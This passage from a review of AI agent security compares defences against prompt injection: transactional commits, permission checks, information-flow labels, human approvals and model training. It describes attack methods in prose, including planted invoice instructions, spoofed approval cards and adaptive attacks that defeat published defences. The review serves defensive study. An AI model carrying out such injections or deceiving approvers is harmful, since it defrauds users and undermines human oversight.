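Here, T is the task, E its outside effects, and W and D its writes and deletions. C_t is the user's intent, the agent's authority and the system's policy at the moment of the commit, so a permission that Ana withdrew halfway through the task no longer counts.

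In the paper's example, an agent reads server logs that contain a secret key, summarises them, writes a note and prepares a Slack message. Each call looks reasonable by itself. At the commit, the lineage connects the message to the key, so Cordon can both block the message and discard the note. A rule engine that blocked the final call would leave the note in place.

Chen and colleagues wrote 45 workflows in which the harm depends on a combination of steps. An unprotected agent caused the harm in all 45. Imitations of existing defences prevented it in 14 and detected it too late in another 5, while Cordon prevented it in all 45. The researchers designed the workflows to target the gap in existing defences that Cordon fills, and they don't report any attacks revised to get past Cordon.

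Average task time rose from 25.6 to 31.4 seconds when a person approved each risky action, including the wait for approval, and fell to 23.6 seconds when every risky action was rejected. Token use fell by about a quarter in both cases. On harmless tasks from two standard benchmarks, the agent did as well as before. Undoing a failed step took a median of 4 milliseconds and left no stray changes, whereas a `git reset` left a median of 73.

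These guarantees end at the outbox. If the computer crashes while sending a payment, Cordon resends it only if there is evidence that the first attempt failed. Cordon also cannot hold back actions by tools that bypass it. An agent repairing a live server could not work this way, for the reason Lyu and colleagues give. The tests did not include several agents competing for the same data.

### Permissions that go out of date

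The budget is both shared data and part of an access rule. Peng and Wu (2026), in *Stateful Governance for Concurrent Agentic Systems*, call the failure in the timeline stale authorization: the system acts on permission after the facts behind it have changed. Suppose that Ana's payment comes from one account and Ben's from another. They don't write to the same account, so an ordinary conflict check may find nothing wrong. They conflict because

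W(Ana's payment) ∩ R(Ben's permission check) ≠ ∅,

where W is the set of facts that the payment changes and R is the set that the check reads. Both contain the budget.

The paper's system, MasuGate, locks those facts from the permission check until the payment commits. In one test, 256 simultaneous payments competed for a budget that could cover 50. About 81 went through when AWS's Cedar decided each request separately, compared with exactly 50 under MasuGate. In a second test, which used a scripted purchasing process with no language model, Microsoft's Agent Governance Toolkit completed 71.6 purchases on average, of which 59.0 were valid, while MasuGate completed 70.6, all valid.

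Waiting for a person's approval makes the problem worse. Ana may approve a payment an hour after her assistant requested it, when Ben has already spent the money. MasuGate can check the budget again, which is safe but wastes her approval, or set aside €700 as soon as the request arrives. In tests where other payments competed for the same budget, checking again invalidated every pending approval, while setting money aside preserved them all. MasuGate's locks slow the system down. When each action took 10 milliseconds, it still handled 86 actions per second, compared with 53 for a single lock on the whole system. With no such delay, MasuGate was 13% slower.

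The guarantee fails if anyone can change the budget without going through MasuGate. The prototype also keeps payments and the budget in one database, and the paper leaves a safe procedure for an outside bank to future work.

Such failures occur in real products. Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects*, examined 17 security advisories from three agent products. In 12, the approval did not cover what the agent actually did. In the other 5, the approval remained in force after the facts behind it had changed. Santos-Grueiro then tested five models whose prompt stated the authorisation rule. A timely notice that an approval had changed prevented nearly all unauthorised actions by the GPT, Fable and Sonnet models, and fewer by the other two. Without a notice, all five mostly went ahead, even when they could have discovered the change by rereading the record. Santos-Grueiro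 proposes that the service performing the action check the approval and act in one indivisible step.

### ACID for agents

Database textbooks summarise the duties of a transaction as ACID. Sun, Wang and Li (2026), in *Agentic Transaction*, redefine each letter for agents.

| Property | In a database | For an agent |
|---|---|---|
| Atomicity | all of a transaction's writes take effect, or none do | model calls, edits and outside actions succeed as a group, or the system undoes or compensates for those it can |
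| Consistency | committed data obey the declared rules | the steps may vary between runs, but the result must meet the task's conditions and rest on evidence |
| Isolation | simultaneous transactions do not disturb one another | agents do not disturb one another's files, memory or context beyond what a stated policy allows |
| Durability | committed data survive a crash | results, evidence and recovery records survive outside the model's context |

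One data-analysis agent works in short cycles of exploring files, running code and validating the outcome. Only validated cycles change its workspace and memory. As part of validation, a small model estimates how much more likely the code becomes when the model's context includes evidence from the files. If the evidence makes little difference, the agent tries again. It may also retry after an execution error or a critical review by a language model.

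Sun and colleagues compared it with Claude Code on KramaBench, which has 104 data-analysis tasks. When both used the model Qwen3.5, it scored 74.6% and Claude Code scored 64.0%. With GLM-5.2, it scored 77.4% and Claude Code scored 74.2%. It took more than twice as many coding steps as Claude Code. It also cost more per task, at $0.10 versus $0.08 with Qwen3.5 and $0.61 versus $0.12 with GLM-5.2.

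On one group of tasks, the score fell from 90.0% to 78.3% when failed attempts could alter the workspace and memory. This is good evidence for discarding the changes made by failed attempts. The experiments did not test isolation between simultaneous agents, so they provide no evidence about the two payments.

### Committing a belief to memory

MemTX applies transactions to memory entries. In this system, which Li and colleagues designed for agents that share a memory, a new entry begins as a draft that other agents normally cannot see. Before committing it, code makes four checks:

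1. The writer is confident enough, or the source has enough authority.
2. The entry is valid at the present time.
3. It does not conflict with another value or expose private material.
4. None of its sources is awaiting withdrawal.

The third check catches the false budget record. Both assistants started from a recorded budget of €1,000. Once Ana's assistant has committed "€300 left", the same entry from Ben's assistant is out of date, and code rejects it regardless of its source's authority.

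MemTX also blocks irreversible tools while certain drafts, including the agent's own, are pending. Ben's assistant therefore has to settle its entry before it pays, so it learns about the conflict before paying. But after the entry is rejected, no draft remains and the rule as defined would allow the payment, so the team still needs a rule about the budget itself.

When someone withdraws an entry, MemTX also revokes or hides the entries derived from it. If an agent has already acted on the entry, MemTX logs that somebody must reverse the action, or that the action is irreversible. It does not reverse the action itself.

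Li and colleagues wrote 90 test cases, 60 with a trap and 30 without, and compared MemTX with eight alternatives on five models. MemTX scored highest on four of them. With Qwen3-8B, it succeeded in 95.6% of cases and the best alternative in 82.2%. With GPT-5.5, the strongest model, MemTX scored 75.6% and the best alternative 77.8%, a statistical tie. On 56 harder cases, GPT-5.5 scored 92.9% with MemTX and 76.8% with the best alternative. In 24 further refund scenarios, only MemTX avoided every wrong refund on all five models. It used up to 14% more tokens than the alternatives. All these cases come from the researchers' own list of memory failures, so the scores don't measure how often such failures occur in practice.

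Every method failed two kinds of case on at least some models. In one, the agent copied private text into a shared summary without recording where it came from, so there was no lineage to check. In the other, an agent whose outdated entry had been rejected submitted it again in a new transaction. That transaction began after the rival entry, so the outdated value no longer counted as late.

### Proofs, measurements and judgement

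| System | Proved or checked exhaustively | Measured only | Left to a model |
|---|---|---|---|
| S-Bus | in the design, every logged read is current at commit | whether the running code matches the design | how to redo rejected work |
| MasuGate | every decision fits some one-at-a-time order | speed, approvals preserved | nothing |
| CoAgent | a sketched proof that the result is serializable | 5 misjudged notices in 100 runs | whether a change matters and what to redo |
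| Cordon | nothing | 45 of 45 workflows stopped | nothing in the commit rule |
| Agentic Transaction | nothing | scores on 104 tasks | whether a step is valid |
| MemTX | no violation in 5.5 million states | success on test cases | which sources an entry declares |

Each system's correctness has been proved or checked only under certain conditions. The proof for S-Bus is machine-checked apart from one basic fact about functions, but it covers only reads in the log. MasuGate's theorem holds only if the people who connect a database declare every fact that a rule reads or an action changes. CoAgent's proof assumes that the model responds correctly to every notice, but in tests it sometimes didn't. MemTX's check covered every state reachable within ten steps with up to four entries and three simultaneous transactions, so it does not rule out faults in larger cases.

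Code also cannot enforce a limit that nobody has stated. If Ana and Ben know about the €1,000 limit but never enter it anywhere, both payments can pass every check. *Tracking State Footprints* (2026) notes that the rules for data outside an agent system are often implicit, and that violations may surface only late, such as when an agent tries to upload its code to a shared repository. How to derive such rules from a user's request is still an open question.

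## Useful work that label rules block, and ways to recover it

Label rules often block work that Ana wants done and that no attacker has touched, as SPA's and CaMeL's losses on AgentDojo show. The main cause is label creep, in which restrictive labels spread to everything an agent does after it reads one restricted item. Typed boundaries can also limit useful work, as with the bug-fixing agent.

### One private read in a task of five steps

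Suppose Ana asks her assistant to check her calendar, look up a supplier's opening hours, ask the supplier for a quote, save the supplier's address in the memory she shares with Ben, and post a reminder to her team. Only the calendar is private, but if the assistant reads it first, the context becomes secret and the other four calls all run under that label.

Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026), in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, measure the damage as the share of calls that either introduce a restrictive label or run under one. If the only private read is step k of n, that share is

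(n − k + 1) / n.

The share is 100% (5/5) when the calendar is read first and 20% (1/5) when it is read last, with an average of 60% over all five positions. A planner can therefore help by putting private reads late in the plan, but this doesn't work if the supplier needs to know which day Ana is free.

Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026) prove in *APPA* that if a call is blocked because the context is too untrusted or too few people are allowed to read it, further reading cannot unblock it, since each new item can only lower the context's trust level or remove permitted readers.

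Labelling smaller pieces of data slows label creep. *AgentKernel* (2026) describes a system that labels each memory item separately, because one label for a whole session is safe but makes interactive work impractical. However, carefully written text may obscure which source an item came from, and the item then gets too lenient a label.

### Dividing the task among agents

A company can also give the calendar to one agent and the web to another, so that a label on one agent's context doesn't restrict the other agent. Gregory and colleagues simulated more than 9,000 abstract tasks to measure how much this helps. Each task was a random set of up to 20 tool calls, some of which needed the output of others. An agent kept the strictest label it encountered, even if it only relayed a message between two other agents.

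They compared ten ways of connecting the agents: a mesh that links every pair, a ring, a star around an orchestrator, a hierarchy with managers, five random networks, and an ideal layout with exactly the links each task needs. Denser networks ran fewer calls under a restrictive label, because agents with direct links need relays less. The rank correlation between density and loss reached −0.96, but it rests on nine data points, since the ideal layout changes with every task and has no fixed density. With four sensitive calls out of 20, the star restricted about 5 percentage points more calls than the ideal layout, and the ring about 3.

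Adding agents also reduced the spread of labels, but someone has to monitor the links between them. A mesh of n agents has n(n − 1)/2 links, so going from 5 agents to 20 raises the number of links from 10 to 190. Grouping the sensitive tools in a few agents, such as one that does all the banking, helped in every layout. No layout removed the loss, because a step that needs private data has to carry the private label wherever it runs.

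The simulation contained no language model, so it shows how labels spread but not how many tasks fail. It counts a restricted call as a loss even if the policy would allow it or a model would have found another way to do the job. It also assumes that agents delegate without mistakes, but real agents may misunderstand one another, and twenty agents have more chances to do so than five.

### Planning with the labels in view

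A person can remove a label that the layout can't. Ana does this by endorsing the data, and later calls based on it then go through without her approval. She can also approve a single tool call that the rules would refuse, but this leaves the labels unchanged. Suppose an e-mail lists ten jobs, each of which needs a consequential tool call. Once the planner has read the e-mail, Ana would have to approve each of the ten calls. If she endorses the e-mail first, she only has to make that one decision.

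*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) presents Prudentia, an agent built around this choice. It extends FIDES, whose planner isn't given the rules and may open a hidden variable needlessly, which causes its next calls to be refused. Prudentia's planner is given the rule for each tool and tracks the label on its own context, though ordinary code still checks each call. Before opening a variable, the planner is instructed to call a `plan` tool, give a reason and list the calls it expects to make afterwards. It then asks the user for an endorsement, or opens the variable without one if nothing consequential will follow.

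Prudentia has no equivalent shortcut for secrets. Whether Ana may share part of her calendar depends on who is asking and why, so she approves each message separately.

Kolluri and colleagues also propose a different way to keep score. Let v(τ) be the number of times a run τ needs a person. Then

TCR@k = the share of tasks completed with v(τ) ≤ k.

TCR@0 is the share of tasks an agent completes alone. They argue that earlier papers compared protected agents at k = 0 with unprotected ones at unlimited k, although many commercial agents ask permission before every consequential action. The table gives their AgentDojo results for GPT-5 without attacks, averaged over five runs.

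| Agent | Completed with unlimited help | Completed alone | Interventions in completed tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Asks before every consequential call | 72.3% | 35.1% | 52.0 |
| Labels, without hidden variables | 72.3% | 43.4% | 40.4 |
| FIDES | 78.9% | 57.1% | 41.3 |
| Prudentia | 80.0% | 72.7% | 7.3 |

This large gain depends on the model. With the older GPT-4o, Prudentia needed 23.8 interventions compared with 7.8 for FIDES, completed fewer tasks alone (42.5% against 50.3%), and cost roughly twice as much.

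On WASP, a benchmark in which an agent browses simulated GitLab and Reddit sites, attacks diverted an ordinary agent in 14.6% to 61.1% of cases, depending on the model and the site. No attack diverted Prudentia, which needed no human intervention and completed at least as many tasks as the ordinary agent with every model. FIDES did about as well as Prudentia. WASP is an easy test for Prudentia's design because neither of its two user tasks, commenting on a post and upvoting one, requires the planner to read what a stranger wrote.

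The researchers ran these experiments without human participants. They counted the calls that would have needed approval and assumed that a person would allow the legitimate ones and stop the rest. That assumption matters more for an endorsement than for an approval. If Ana endorses the invoice e-mail, the thief's account number becomes trusted along with everything else in it, and the payment rule no longer blocks a payment to that account. With ten separate approvals, she would at least have had ten chances to notice something wrong.

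APPA keeps exceptions narrower, since an approval covers one exact call, once, and changes no label. To avoid needing approvals, the agent can start a temporary branch, which inherits the agent's label, reads the untrusted text and returns only a typed value. As with any typed answer, the value may be false, so the developer has to decide whether to trust it. When APPA refuses a call, it also suggests a permitted step that would clear the refusal, if it finds one. On 20 company workflows that Kravchenko and colleagues wrote themselves, GPT-5.6 Luna completed 88% of runs. Without branches it completed 56.5%, and without the suggestions 35.0%. No attack succeeded in any of the three versions.

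### People who approve everything

Approval fatigue is the tendency to stop reading requests after seeing too many. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026) reports that users approve 97% of the coding agent's permission prompts. Most of those prompts are probably for harmless commands, so the figure alone doesn't prove carelessness.

A test with dangerous commands is better evidence. According to the website Hyrax, which summarises Anthropic's data, testers blocked only 143 of 1,053 (13.6%). The rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. However, users reject 39% of the agent's plans. They may read plans more carefully than commands, or they may often want a different plan.

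Fewer requests may not lead to more careful answers. In a user study, *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026), some participants wrote standing rules that included which actions the agent should ask about. They saw fewer prompts for overreaching actions than the other groups did, but approved more of them. Of the 148 overreaching actions that went ahead in their group, they had personally approved 133. Prudentia clearly saves Ana time by requiring only seven interventions, but nobody has shown that she would judge those seven well.

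Requests are often hard to judge, even for an attentive person. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyses 290 reports of trouble with agents and file systems. User review contributed to 105 of them. In 80, actions had gone through on automatic approval, and in 31 the prompt gave too little information. For example, approving a routine-looking request to run `python3 setup.py` runs whatever the script contains. Ana has the same problem with "Pay €400 to account 55501234", because the request doesn't show whose account it is.

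An attacker can exploit this. In Prudentia, code decides when to ask, so planted text can't suppress the request, but Kolluri and colleagues warn that it might influence the request's wording. *Approve What, Exactly?* (2026) tests approval cards rendered by trusted software. In one attack, an ordinary argument is named "Target" so that it looks like the card's own label for the real target. The cards protected a simulated approver that relied on the agent's explanation only when the software left that explanation out. For Ana's payment, the card should therefore show facts the agent cannot write, such as the account on file and a note that the new number came from an outside e-mail.

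### Graded labels and signed sources

More precise labels would make it easier to ask people less often. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests replacing yes-or-no labels with graded ones that estimate how much each source contributed to an output. One way to estimate this is to remove a source and see whether the output changes.

*Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) shows how such estimates fail. If the thief's account number appears in both the invoice e-mail and its attachment, removing either one changes nothing, so both look irrelevant. Methods that measure how sensitive the output is to small changes in a source have a different weakness. Their signal contains the factor 1 − p, where p is the probability the model gave to its chosen token. At p = 0.99, this factor is 0.01, so a source that fully determined a confident answer may seem to have had no influence.

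Their tool, Sightline, instead learns from labelled examples which attention patterns indicate that a model used an input, then drops the labels of inputs it classifies as unused. The user sets the share of real influences it may miss on average. On 120 AgentDojo turns, with a target of 5%, Sightline removed half of the unnecessary labels and missed 3.9% of the real influences. A rule against untrusted data still stopped all 34 attack calls.

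The average holds only if new cases resemble the examples, and an attacker can write something that doesn't. Any such method is also limited in what it can recover. In calls to models from more than 2,000 groups of open-source projects, only 12% to 14% of the inputs had no effect on the output. The labels from the other inputs were correct, so dropping them would have been a mistake. An input that contributes little can still pose a large risk, because a single yes or no can release a payment.

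Verifying the source of data might justify a looser label. If the paper supplier signed its invoices and Ana's company already had the key to verify them, a policy could accept account numbers from signed invoices, and a thief who only imitated the supplier's e-mails would fail. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* gives signed software documentation as an example, but cautions that a signature shows where something came from, not that it is safe. It therefore calls for an explicit policy to authorise each relaxation, with the usual checks still running.

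### When a stranger's text has to decide

Suppose Ana types, "If a customer reports a fault, refund the order." The order number and amount can come from her own records, but the agent can find out whether there was a fault only from the customer's e-mail. Because the refund is in a branch that depends on the e-mail, a system such as the one by Girrens and Wang labels the refund untrusted even if each argument is trusted. Requiring a trusted decision will block every refund, but without that requirement anyone who claims a fault will get one.

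Narisetty and colleagues call tasks like this the deepest open problem for such defences, and write that nobody has a principled account of which ones can be made secure. The usual answer is to ask the user, which brings back user fatigue and the risk that an attacker will deceive the user. Prudentia reduced the number of interventions on AgentDojo's data-dependent tasks by a factor of up to 2.5, but couldn't eliminate them.

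Ana can limit the damage without determining whether a report is true. Her developer could let the quarantined model return only a yes or no, and have ordinary code confirm that the customer paid for the order and hasn't already received a refund. The code could send the money only to the card used for the order, up to a daily limit. An outsider could no longer send a refund to a new account, but a customer who lied about a fault would still get the money back.

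## Comparison with treating the model as a black box

No rule in code can tell whether a customer who reports a fault is lying, so a model or a person has to judge the report. Developers who treat the model as a black box rely on its judgement for everything the agent does, and the best models have become much harder to deceive since 2025. How this approach compares with enforced rules depends on how well the model resists a persistent attacker.

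### Prompts, detectors, hidden tests and training

*Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) compares four kinds of black-box defence. The simplest is a special prompt. Spotlighting adds markers that show the model which text came from outside. Prompt sandwiching repeats Ana's request after the invoice, which makes the model less likely to lose track of the request.

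A detector is a separate, usually small model that reads each e-mail or tool result and blocks anything that looks like an attack.

Other defences run a test hidden from the attacker. Data Sentinel tells a model to repeat a secret key and ignore the invoice, and treats the invoice as hostile if the model fails to repeat the key. MELON runs the agent a second time with a harmless request in place of Ana's. If the agent still tries to make the same payment, the instruction to pay probably came from the invoice.

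Some defenses train the model itself. StruQ puts the user's instructions and the outside data in separate parts of the prompt, and trains the model to follow only the user's instructions. SecAlign trains the model to prefer answers that ignore planted instructions. OpenAI uses an instruction hierarchy, which *GPT-Red* (Wallace, Choquette-Choo and colleagues, 2026) describes as a ranking of system, developer and user messages and tool results. When two instructions conflict, the model should follow the higher-ranked one.

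### Twelve defences against adaptive attackers

Most of these defences did well in their original tests, which used fixed lists of attacks or weak automated attacks. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) attacked twelve published defences, adapting their attacks to each one. The attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them, although most of the original papers had reported success rates near zero. Two of the twelve defences were for jailbreaks, and the table shows results for nine of the ten that address prompt injection.

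| Defence | Kind | Success of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting, prompt sandwiching | special prompt | above 95% each |
| Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor | detector | above 90% each |
| PIGuard | detector | 71% |
| MELON | hidden test | 95% |
| StruQ | training | 100% |
| MetaSecAlign, a successor to SecAlign | training | 96% |

Attackers could still make a model protected by Data Sentinel, the tenth defence, do their task instead of the user's, and the model did it about as accurately as it would have with no defence.

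The two prompting defences had let through as few as 1% of AgentDojo's standard attacks, and MetaSecAlign 2%. The adaptive rates come from different benchmarks, so they don't show which defence is best. The attackers also had favourable conditions, including plenty of computing power and access to the detectors' confidence scores. An attacker who didn't know how MELON worked succeeded against it 76% of the time.

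In 2026, He and colleagues made a similar comparison with two small open models, using the most successful fixed attack and the most successful adaptive attack against each defence. On Qwen3-4B, the average success rate across all the defences rose from 21.7% with fixed attacks to 41.8% with adaptive ones. The average rise for the two models was 15.8 percentage points. Some of that rise may come from the choice of cases, because the fixed attacks ran on 420 cases, while the adaptive ones ran on 40 that the researchers had picked out as vulnerable.

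### Newer training

RETA, He and colleagues' own defence, trains a model to reason before each tool call about whether the call follows from the user's request. This check relies on Ana's request, which an attacker cannot change by rewording the invoice. RETA also trains the model on deliberately varied attacks, because a model trained on many versions of one attack may still be vulnerable to others. In tests on two models, each of six adaptive attacks succeeded less than 10% of the time, and the average success rates were 2.9% and 3.8%.

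In a preliminary experiment with simpler training, adding the reasoning step cut one adaptive attack's success rate from 40.0% to 27.5%. The reasoning therefore helps, but much of RETA's improvement probably comes from the rest of its training. The method may also be weaker for a request like Ana's, "Pay the invoice that came in today". She didn't name an account, so paying the thief may seem to follow from her request.

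OpenAI has applied training on a much larger scale. It trained an attacking model, GPT-Red, against a varied group of defending models, and used GPT-Red to make GPT-5.6 more resistant to attack. Wallace and colleagues call this the largest documented safety training run for a language model. On a benchmark of direct prompt injections, GPT-5.6 Sol failed one-sixth as often as GPT-5.5, a model four months older, according to The Hacker News (2026). IT Brief UK reports that GPT-5.6 Sol resisted 99.95% of GPT-Red's direct injections.

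Those figures are impressive, but they are for direct injections, which arrive in the user's own message, whereas Ana's attacker uses an e-mail. The 99.95% also measures resistance to the same attacker that OpenAI used in training. Wallace and colleagues write that robustness "remains far from solved".

### How well current models resist

In November 2026, Kurakin, Karande and colleagues at Google DeepMind published *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms*, which tested models against a stronger attacker. They wrote 100 scenarios in which an agent uses tools for one task and the attacker tries to make it call an unrelated tool. The attacker could make up to 320 attempts per scenario, and a model counted as resisting a scenario only if every attempt failed.

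| Model under attack | Scenarios resisted, first 150 attempts | Scenarios resisted, full budget |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Argon | 87% | 66% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 34% | 10% |
| Gemini 3.7 Flash | 31% | 6% |
| Gemini 3.6 Flash | 3% | 1% |
| Kimi K3 | 5% | 1% |
| GLM-5.3 | 1% | 1% |
| DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash | 1% | 1% |

The differences are large enough to matter when a company chooses a model. The three models at the bottom of the table have open weights and showed almost no resistance, even though they score well on ordinary benchmarks.

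Gemini 4 Argon also ran the attacks in this table. When any of the three Flash models ran them instead, Argon resisted every scenario for the first 150 attempts. An unchanged model can therefore become less resistant after its release as attackers get better models.

Some of the conditions made the attacker's job easier. The goals were harmless, such as recording a health reading during a tutoring task, so a model that can detect theft might resist an attack on Ana's bank account more often. The researchers also switched off the defences that Google places around its Gemini models. The number of attempts is less unrealistic than it looks, because a thief might practise on another copy of the assistant and send Ana only the e-mail that worked, rather than 320 suspicious ones.

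Repeated attempts had a similar effect on an older model, Claude Opus 4.5. According to figures from Anthropic that Narisetty and colleagues cite, attacks on it in coding tasks succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with 100. If each attempt had an independent 4.7% chance of success, the rate after 100 attempts would be

1 − (1 − 0.047)¹⁰⁰ ≈ 99%.

The actual rate was much lower, so the model must have resisted some attacks far more reliably than others. But a single-attempt rate is still a poor measure of what a persistent attacker can do.

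### The same models with and without enforcement

A fair test of enforcement keeps the model and the tasks the same and changes only the rules. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* tests TACIT this way, a system that type-checks an agent's code before running it. The agent worked on a software project with a folder of secrets, including passwords for online services. It received the secrets in a wrapper it could not open when protection was on, and as ordinary text when protection was off.

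Each model went through 131 trials in each mode. In 120, an ordinary task came with a planted instruction. In the other 11, the user tried to get the secrets, sometimes by posing as an administrator.

| | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | MiniMax M2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| No leak, protection on | 100% | 100% |
| No leak, protection off | 98.5% | 91.6% |
| No leak, protection off, planted instructions only | 100% | 97.5% |
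| No leak, protection off, hostile users only | 81.8% | 27.3% |
| Utility, protection on | 99.2% | 90.0% |
| Utility, protection off | 83.3% | 88.3% |

Without protection, the two models leaked secrets 13 times, and 10 of those leaks went to hostile users. Planted instructions caused only three leaks in 240 trials, so the measured benefit of protection was small against prompt injection and much larger against users who weren't allowed to see the secrets. The attacks were fixed in advance. TACIT's advantage is that its protection didn't depend on which model the agent used.

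The protection did not reduce utility. Claude scored higher with protection on, but this may be an accident of the set-up, because without protection it often ran out of time or turns and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an attack.

Zhou and colleagues tested enforcement more severely in ELBA, which type-checks an agent's Haskell code. ELBA's agents read outside data through subagents. The researchers changed the software so that a subagent that encountered an attack received only the attacker's text, with no other task. They then ran AgentDojo's 105 Slack attack cases seven times, for 735 runs per model and setting.

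| Model | Attacks resisted, policies on | Attacks resisted, policies off | Tasks completed, policies on | Tasks completed, policies off |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 735 | 425 | 351 | 523 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 735 | 460 | 312 | 557 |
| GPT-5.4 | 735 | 621 | 338 | 558 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 735 | 540 | 294 | 494 |

This is good evidence that the policies don't need the model's cooperation. AgentDojo scored 29 of the 2,940 protected runs as successful attacks because the agent had opened a particular web address, but Zhou and colleagues checked all 29 by hand and found no security violation.

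With GPT-5.4, the policies prevented 114 successful attacks, but the agent completed 220 fewer tasks. A stolen payment is usually worse than an unfinished task, so a company might accept that tradeoff for a payment tool. The tradeoff would be poor for a tool that can do little harm, especially since these models rarely obey an attacker unless researchers force them to.

### SecAlign compared with a divided agent

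*The Framing Gap* (Rahman and Kim, 2026) compares training the model with changing the agent's structure. The agent summarises a web page while holding a secret that it may send to only one trusted address. The page contains a disguised request to send the secret elsewhere. All the versions in the table used Llama 3.1 8B, a small model from 2024, and SecAlign was a further-trained copy of it.

| Defence | Attacks that leaked the secret |
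|---|---|
| None | 21.2% |
| Outside text in a separate part of the prompt | 38.8% |
| SecAlign | 32.5% |
| Separate planner and reader, as in CaMeL | 0% |
| List of permitted destinations | 0% |

SecAlign worked against the simple kind of attack that its training covers. The original model obeyed one such attack in all 20 trials, and SecAlign obeyed it in none. That resistance did not extend to the disguised requests. SecAlign had a higher rate than the undefended model, but this is only weak evidence that it made matters worse, because Rahman and Kim ran each version once, and two identical runs of an earlier experiment had given 31.9% and 40.0%.

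The two zeros follow from the designs. The divided agent gives the secret only to the planner and the hostile page only to the reader. It still produced acceptable summaries in nine of ten harmless trials, but this task suits it unusually well because the planner doesn't need to know what the page contains. The destination list stops the leak however the attacker words the request, but it also blocks legitimate messages to unlisted addresses.

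A check written in code is still unreliable if it checks the wrong thing. In *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models*, Deep, Emmons and colleagues (2026) attacked chatbots that had secrets in their instructions. Every defence that relied on the model eventually leaked, while a filter that searched the chatbot's answers for text from those instructions had no recorded leaks in 15,000 attacks. But the researchers, most of whom work for a company that sells security tools, also measured leaks by searching for exact text, so their test would have missed a secret in an altered form.

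Rahman and Kim tested GPT-4o with attacks that made the model alter the secret before sending it. A filter for the exact text reduced the leak rate only from 56.7% to 50.0%. A rule about where data may go avoids this problem because it doesn't have to recognise the secret.

### Typed code and ordinary tool calls

Enforcement might still not be worth using if it made agents worse at ordinary work. The TACIT evaluation compared agents that wrote typed Scala programs with agents that called tools one at a time. It ran each of the airline and retail tasks in τ²-bench ten times.

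| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, typed code | Retail, tool calls | Retail, typed code |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

Typed code did better in all six comparisons, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. The designers credit the compiler's error messages and the clearer structure of the data that tools return. The experiment can't separate those benefits from the benefit of writing programs at all, because none of its agents wrote untyped code.

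On the 300 problems in SWE-bench Lite, MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7% with typed code and 43.3% with ordinary tools, a difference of five problems. The designers suggest that general programming depends more on shell commands, which are harder to express through TACIT's library. Together, these results suggest that typed code reduces reliability only slightly on tasks with well-defined tools, and perhaps a little more on open-ended programming.

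Typed programs can also save computation. In Zhou and colleagues' bibliography test, where ELBA prevented invented citations, the ordinary agent made about four times as many model calls as ELBA's agent and used 65 times as many input tokens. The tools may explain part of the difference, since ELBA's agent fetched finished entries from a database, while the ordinary agent wrote its own from search results.

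These comparisons don't include the performance loss from strict data policies, which is often much larger, as the ELBA results with and without policies show.

### Advantages of relying on the model

Current models already resist familiar attacks well. In Zhou and colleagues' main tests, without the forced obedience, four models resisted every standard AgentDojo attack in the Slack suite even when ELBA's policies were off. ELBA still read outside data through subagents in those tests, which may have helped. But Peters-Gill and colleagues saw no successful AgentDojo attack on GPT-5.5 in an agent with no defence. For a low-risk assistant facing only opportunistic attackers, the model's own resistance may be enough.

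A product can resist attacks better than the model inside it. Rahman and Kim tried some of their attack pages on ChatGPT and saw no leaks in 48 trials, although some of the same attacks always worked on GPT-4o through OpenAI's API. They could not tell whether the difference came from a different model, a detector, or some other safeguard around the model.

Training can also reduce harm from text, which rules about actions don't cover. Suppose Ana asks for a summary of a supplier's web page, and an instruction planted in the page makes the model leave out a safety warning. The assistant makes no forbidden tool call, so a payment rule has nothing to block. CaMeL's goals exclude this kind of harm. A model that has learned to ignore instructions in outside text might still give Ana an accurate summary. OpenAI's work with GPT-Red also covers requests for harmful content, such as advice on self-harm.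 Neither kind of training helps much if the page contains a believable lie.

A developer can adopt a better-trained model without redesigning the agent, labelling its data or writing policies. Google DeepMind (2025) reports that such training made attacks on Gemini less successful without significantly affecting its performance on normal tasks, but warns that "no model is completely immune".

A model can also distinguish cases that simple rules can't. A label rule treats genuine and forged invoices alike, while a good model may flag a supplier's new account number as suspicious. This flexibility explains much of why black-box agents complete tasks that rule-bound agents don't.

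### Few adaptive tests of enforced rules

Black-box defences have failed many adaptive tests, but few such tests have been run on structured defences. He et al. left systems such as CaMeL out of their comparison because a fair test would need tasks in which both security and usefulness depend on untrusted text. Narisetty et al. warn that confidence in structured defences comes largely from fixed benchmarks, on which black-box defences had also looked strong.

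They ran a small adaptive test on Progent, the rule engine that has a model write rules for each task. Their attack was meant to persuade that model to permit the harmful call. The agent used Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, on eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo suites. The table shows average attack success over three runs.

| Suite | No defence, standard attack | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
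|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Workspace | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Average | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

The adaptive attack did worse than the standard one on average, which suggests that it was weak. Narisetty and colleagues think its milder wording may have made the agent itself less likely to obey. The Workspace suite adds nothing to the comparison, because no attack succeeded there even without a defence. Progent also lowered the share of tasks completed under attack from 45.2% to 27.1%, and the agent made about 15 times as many model calls.

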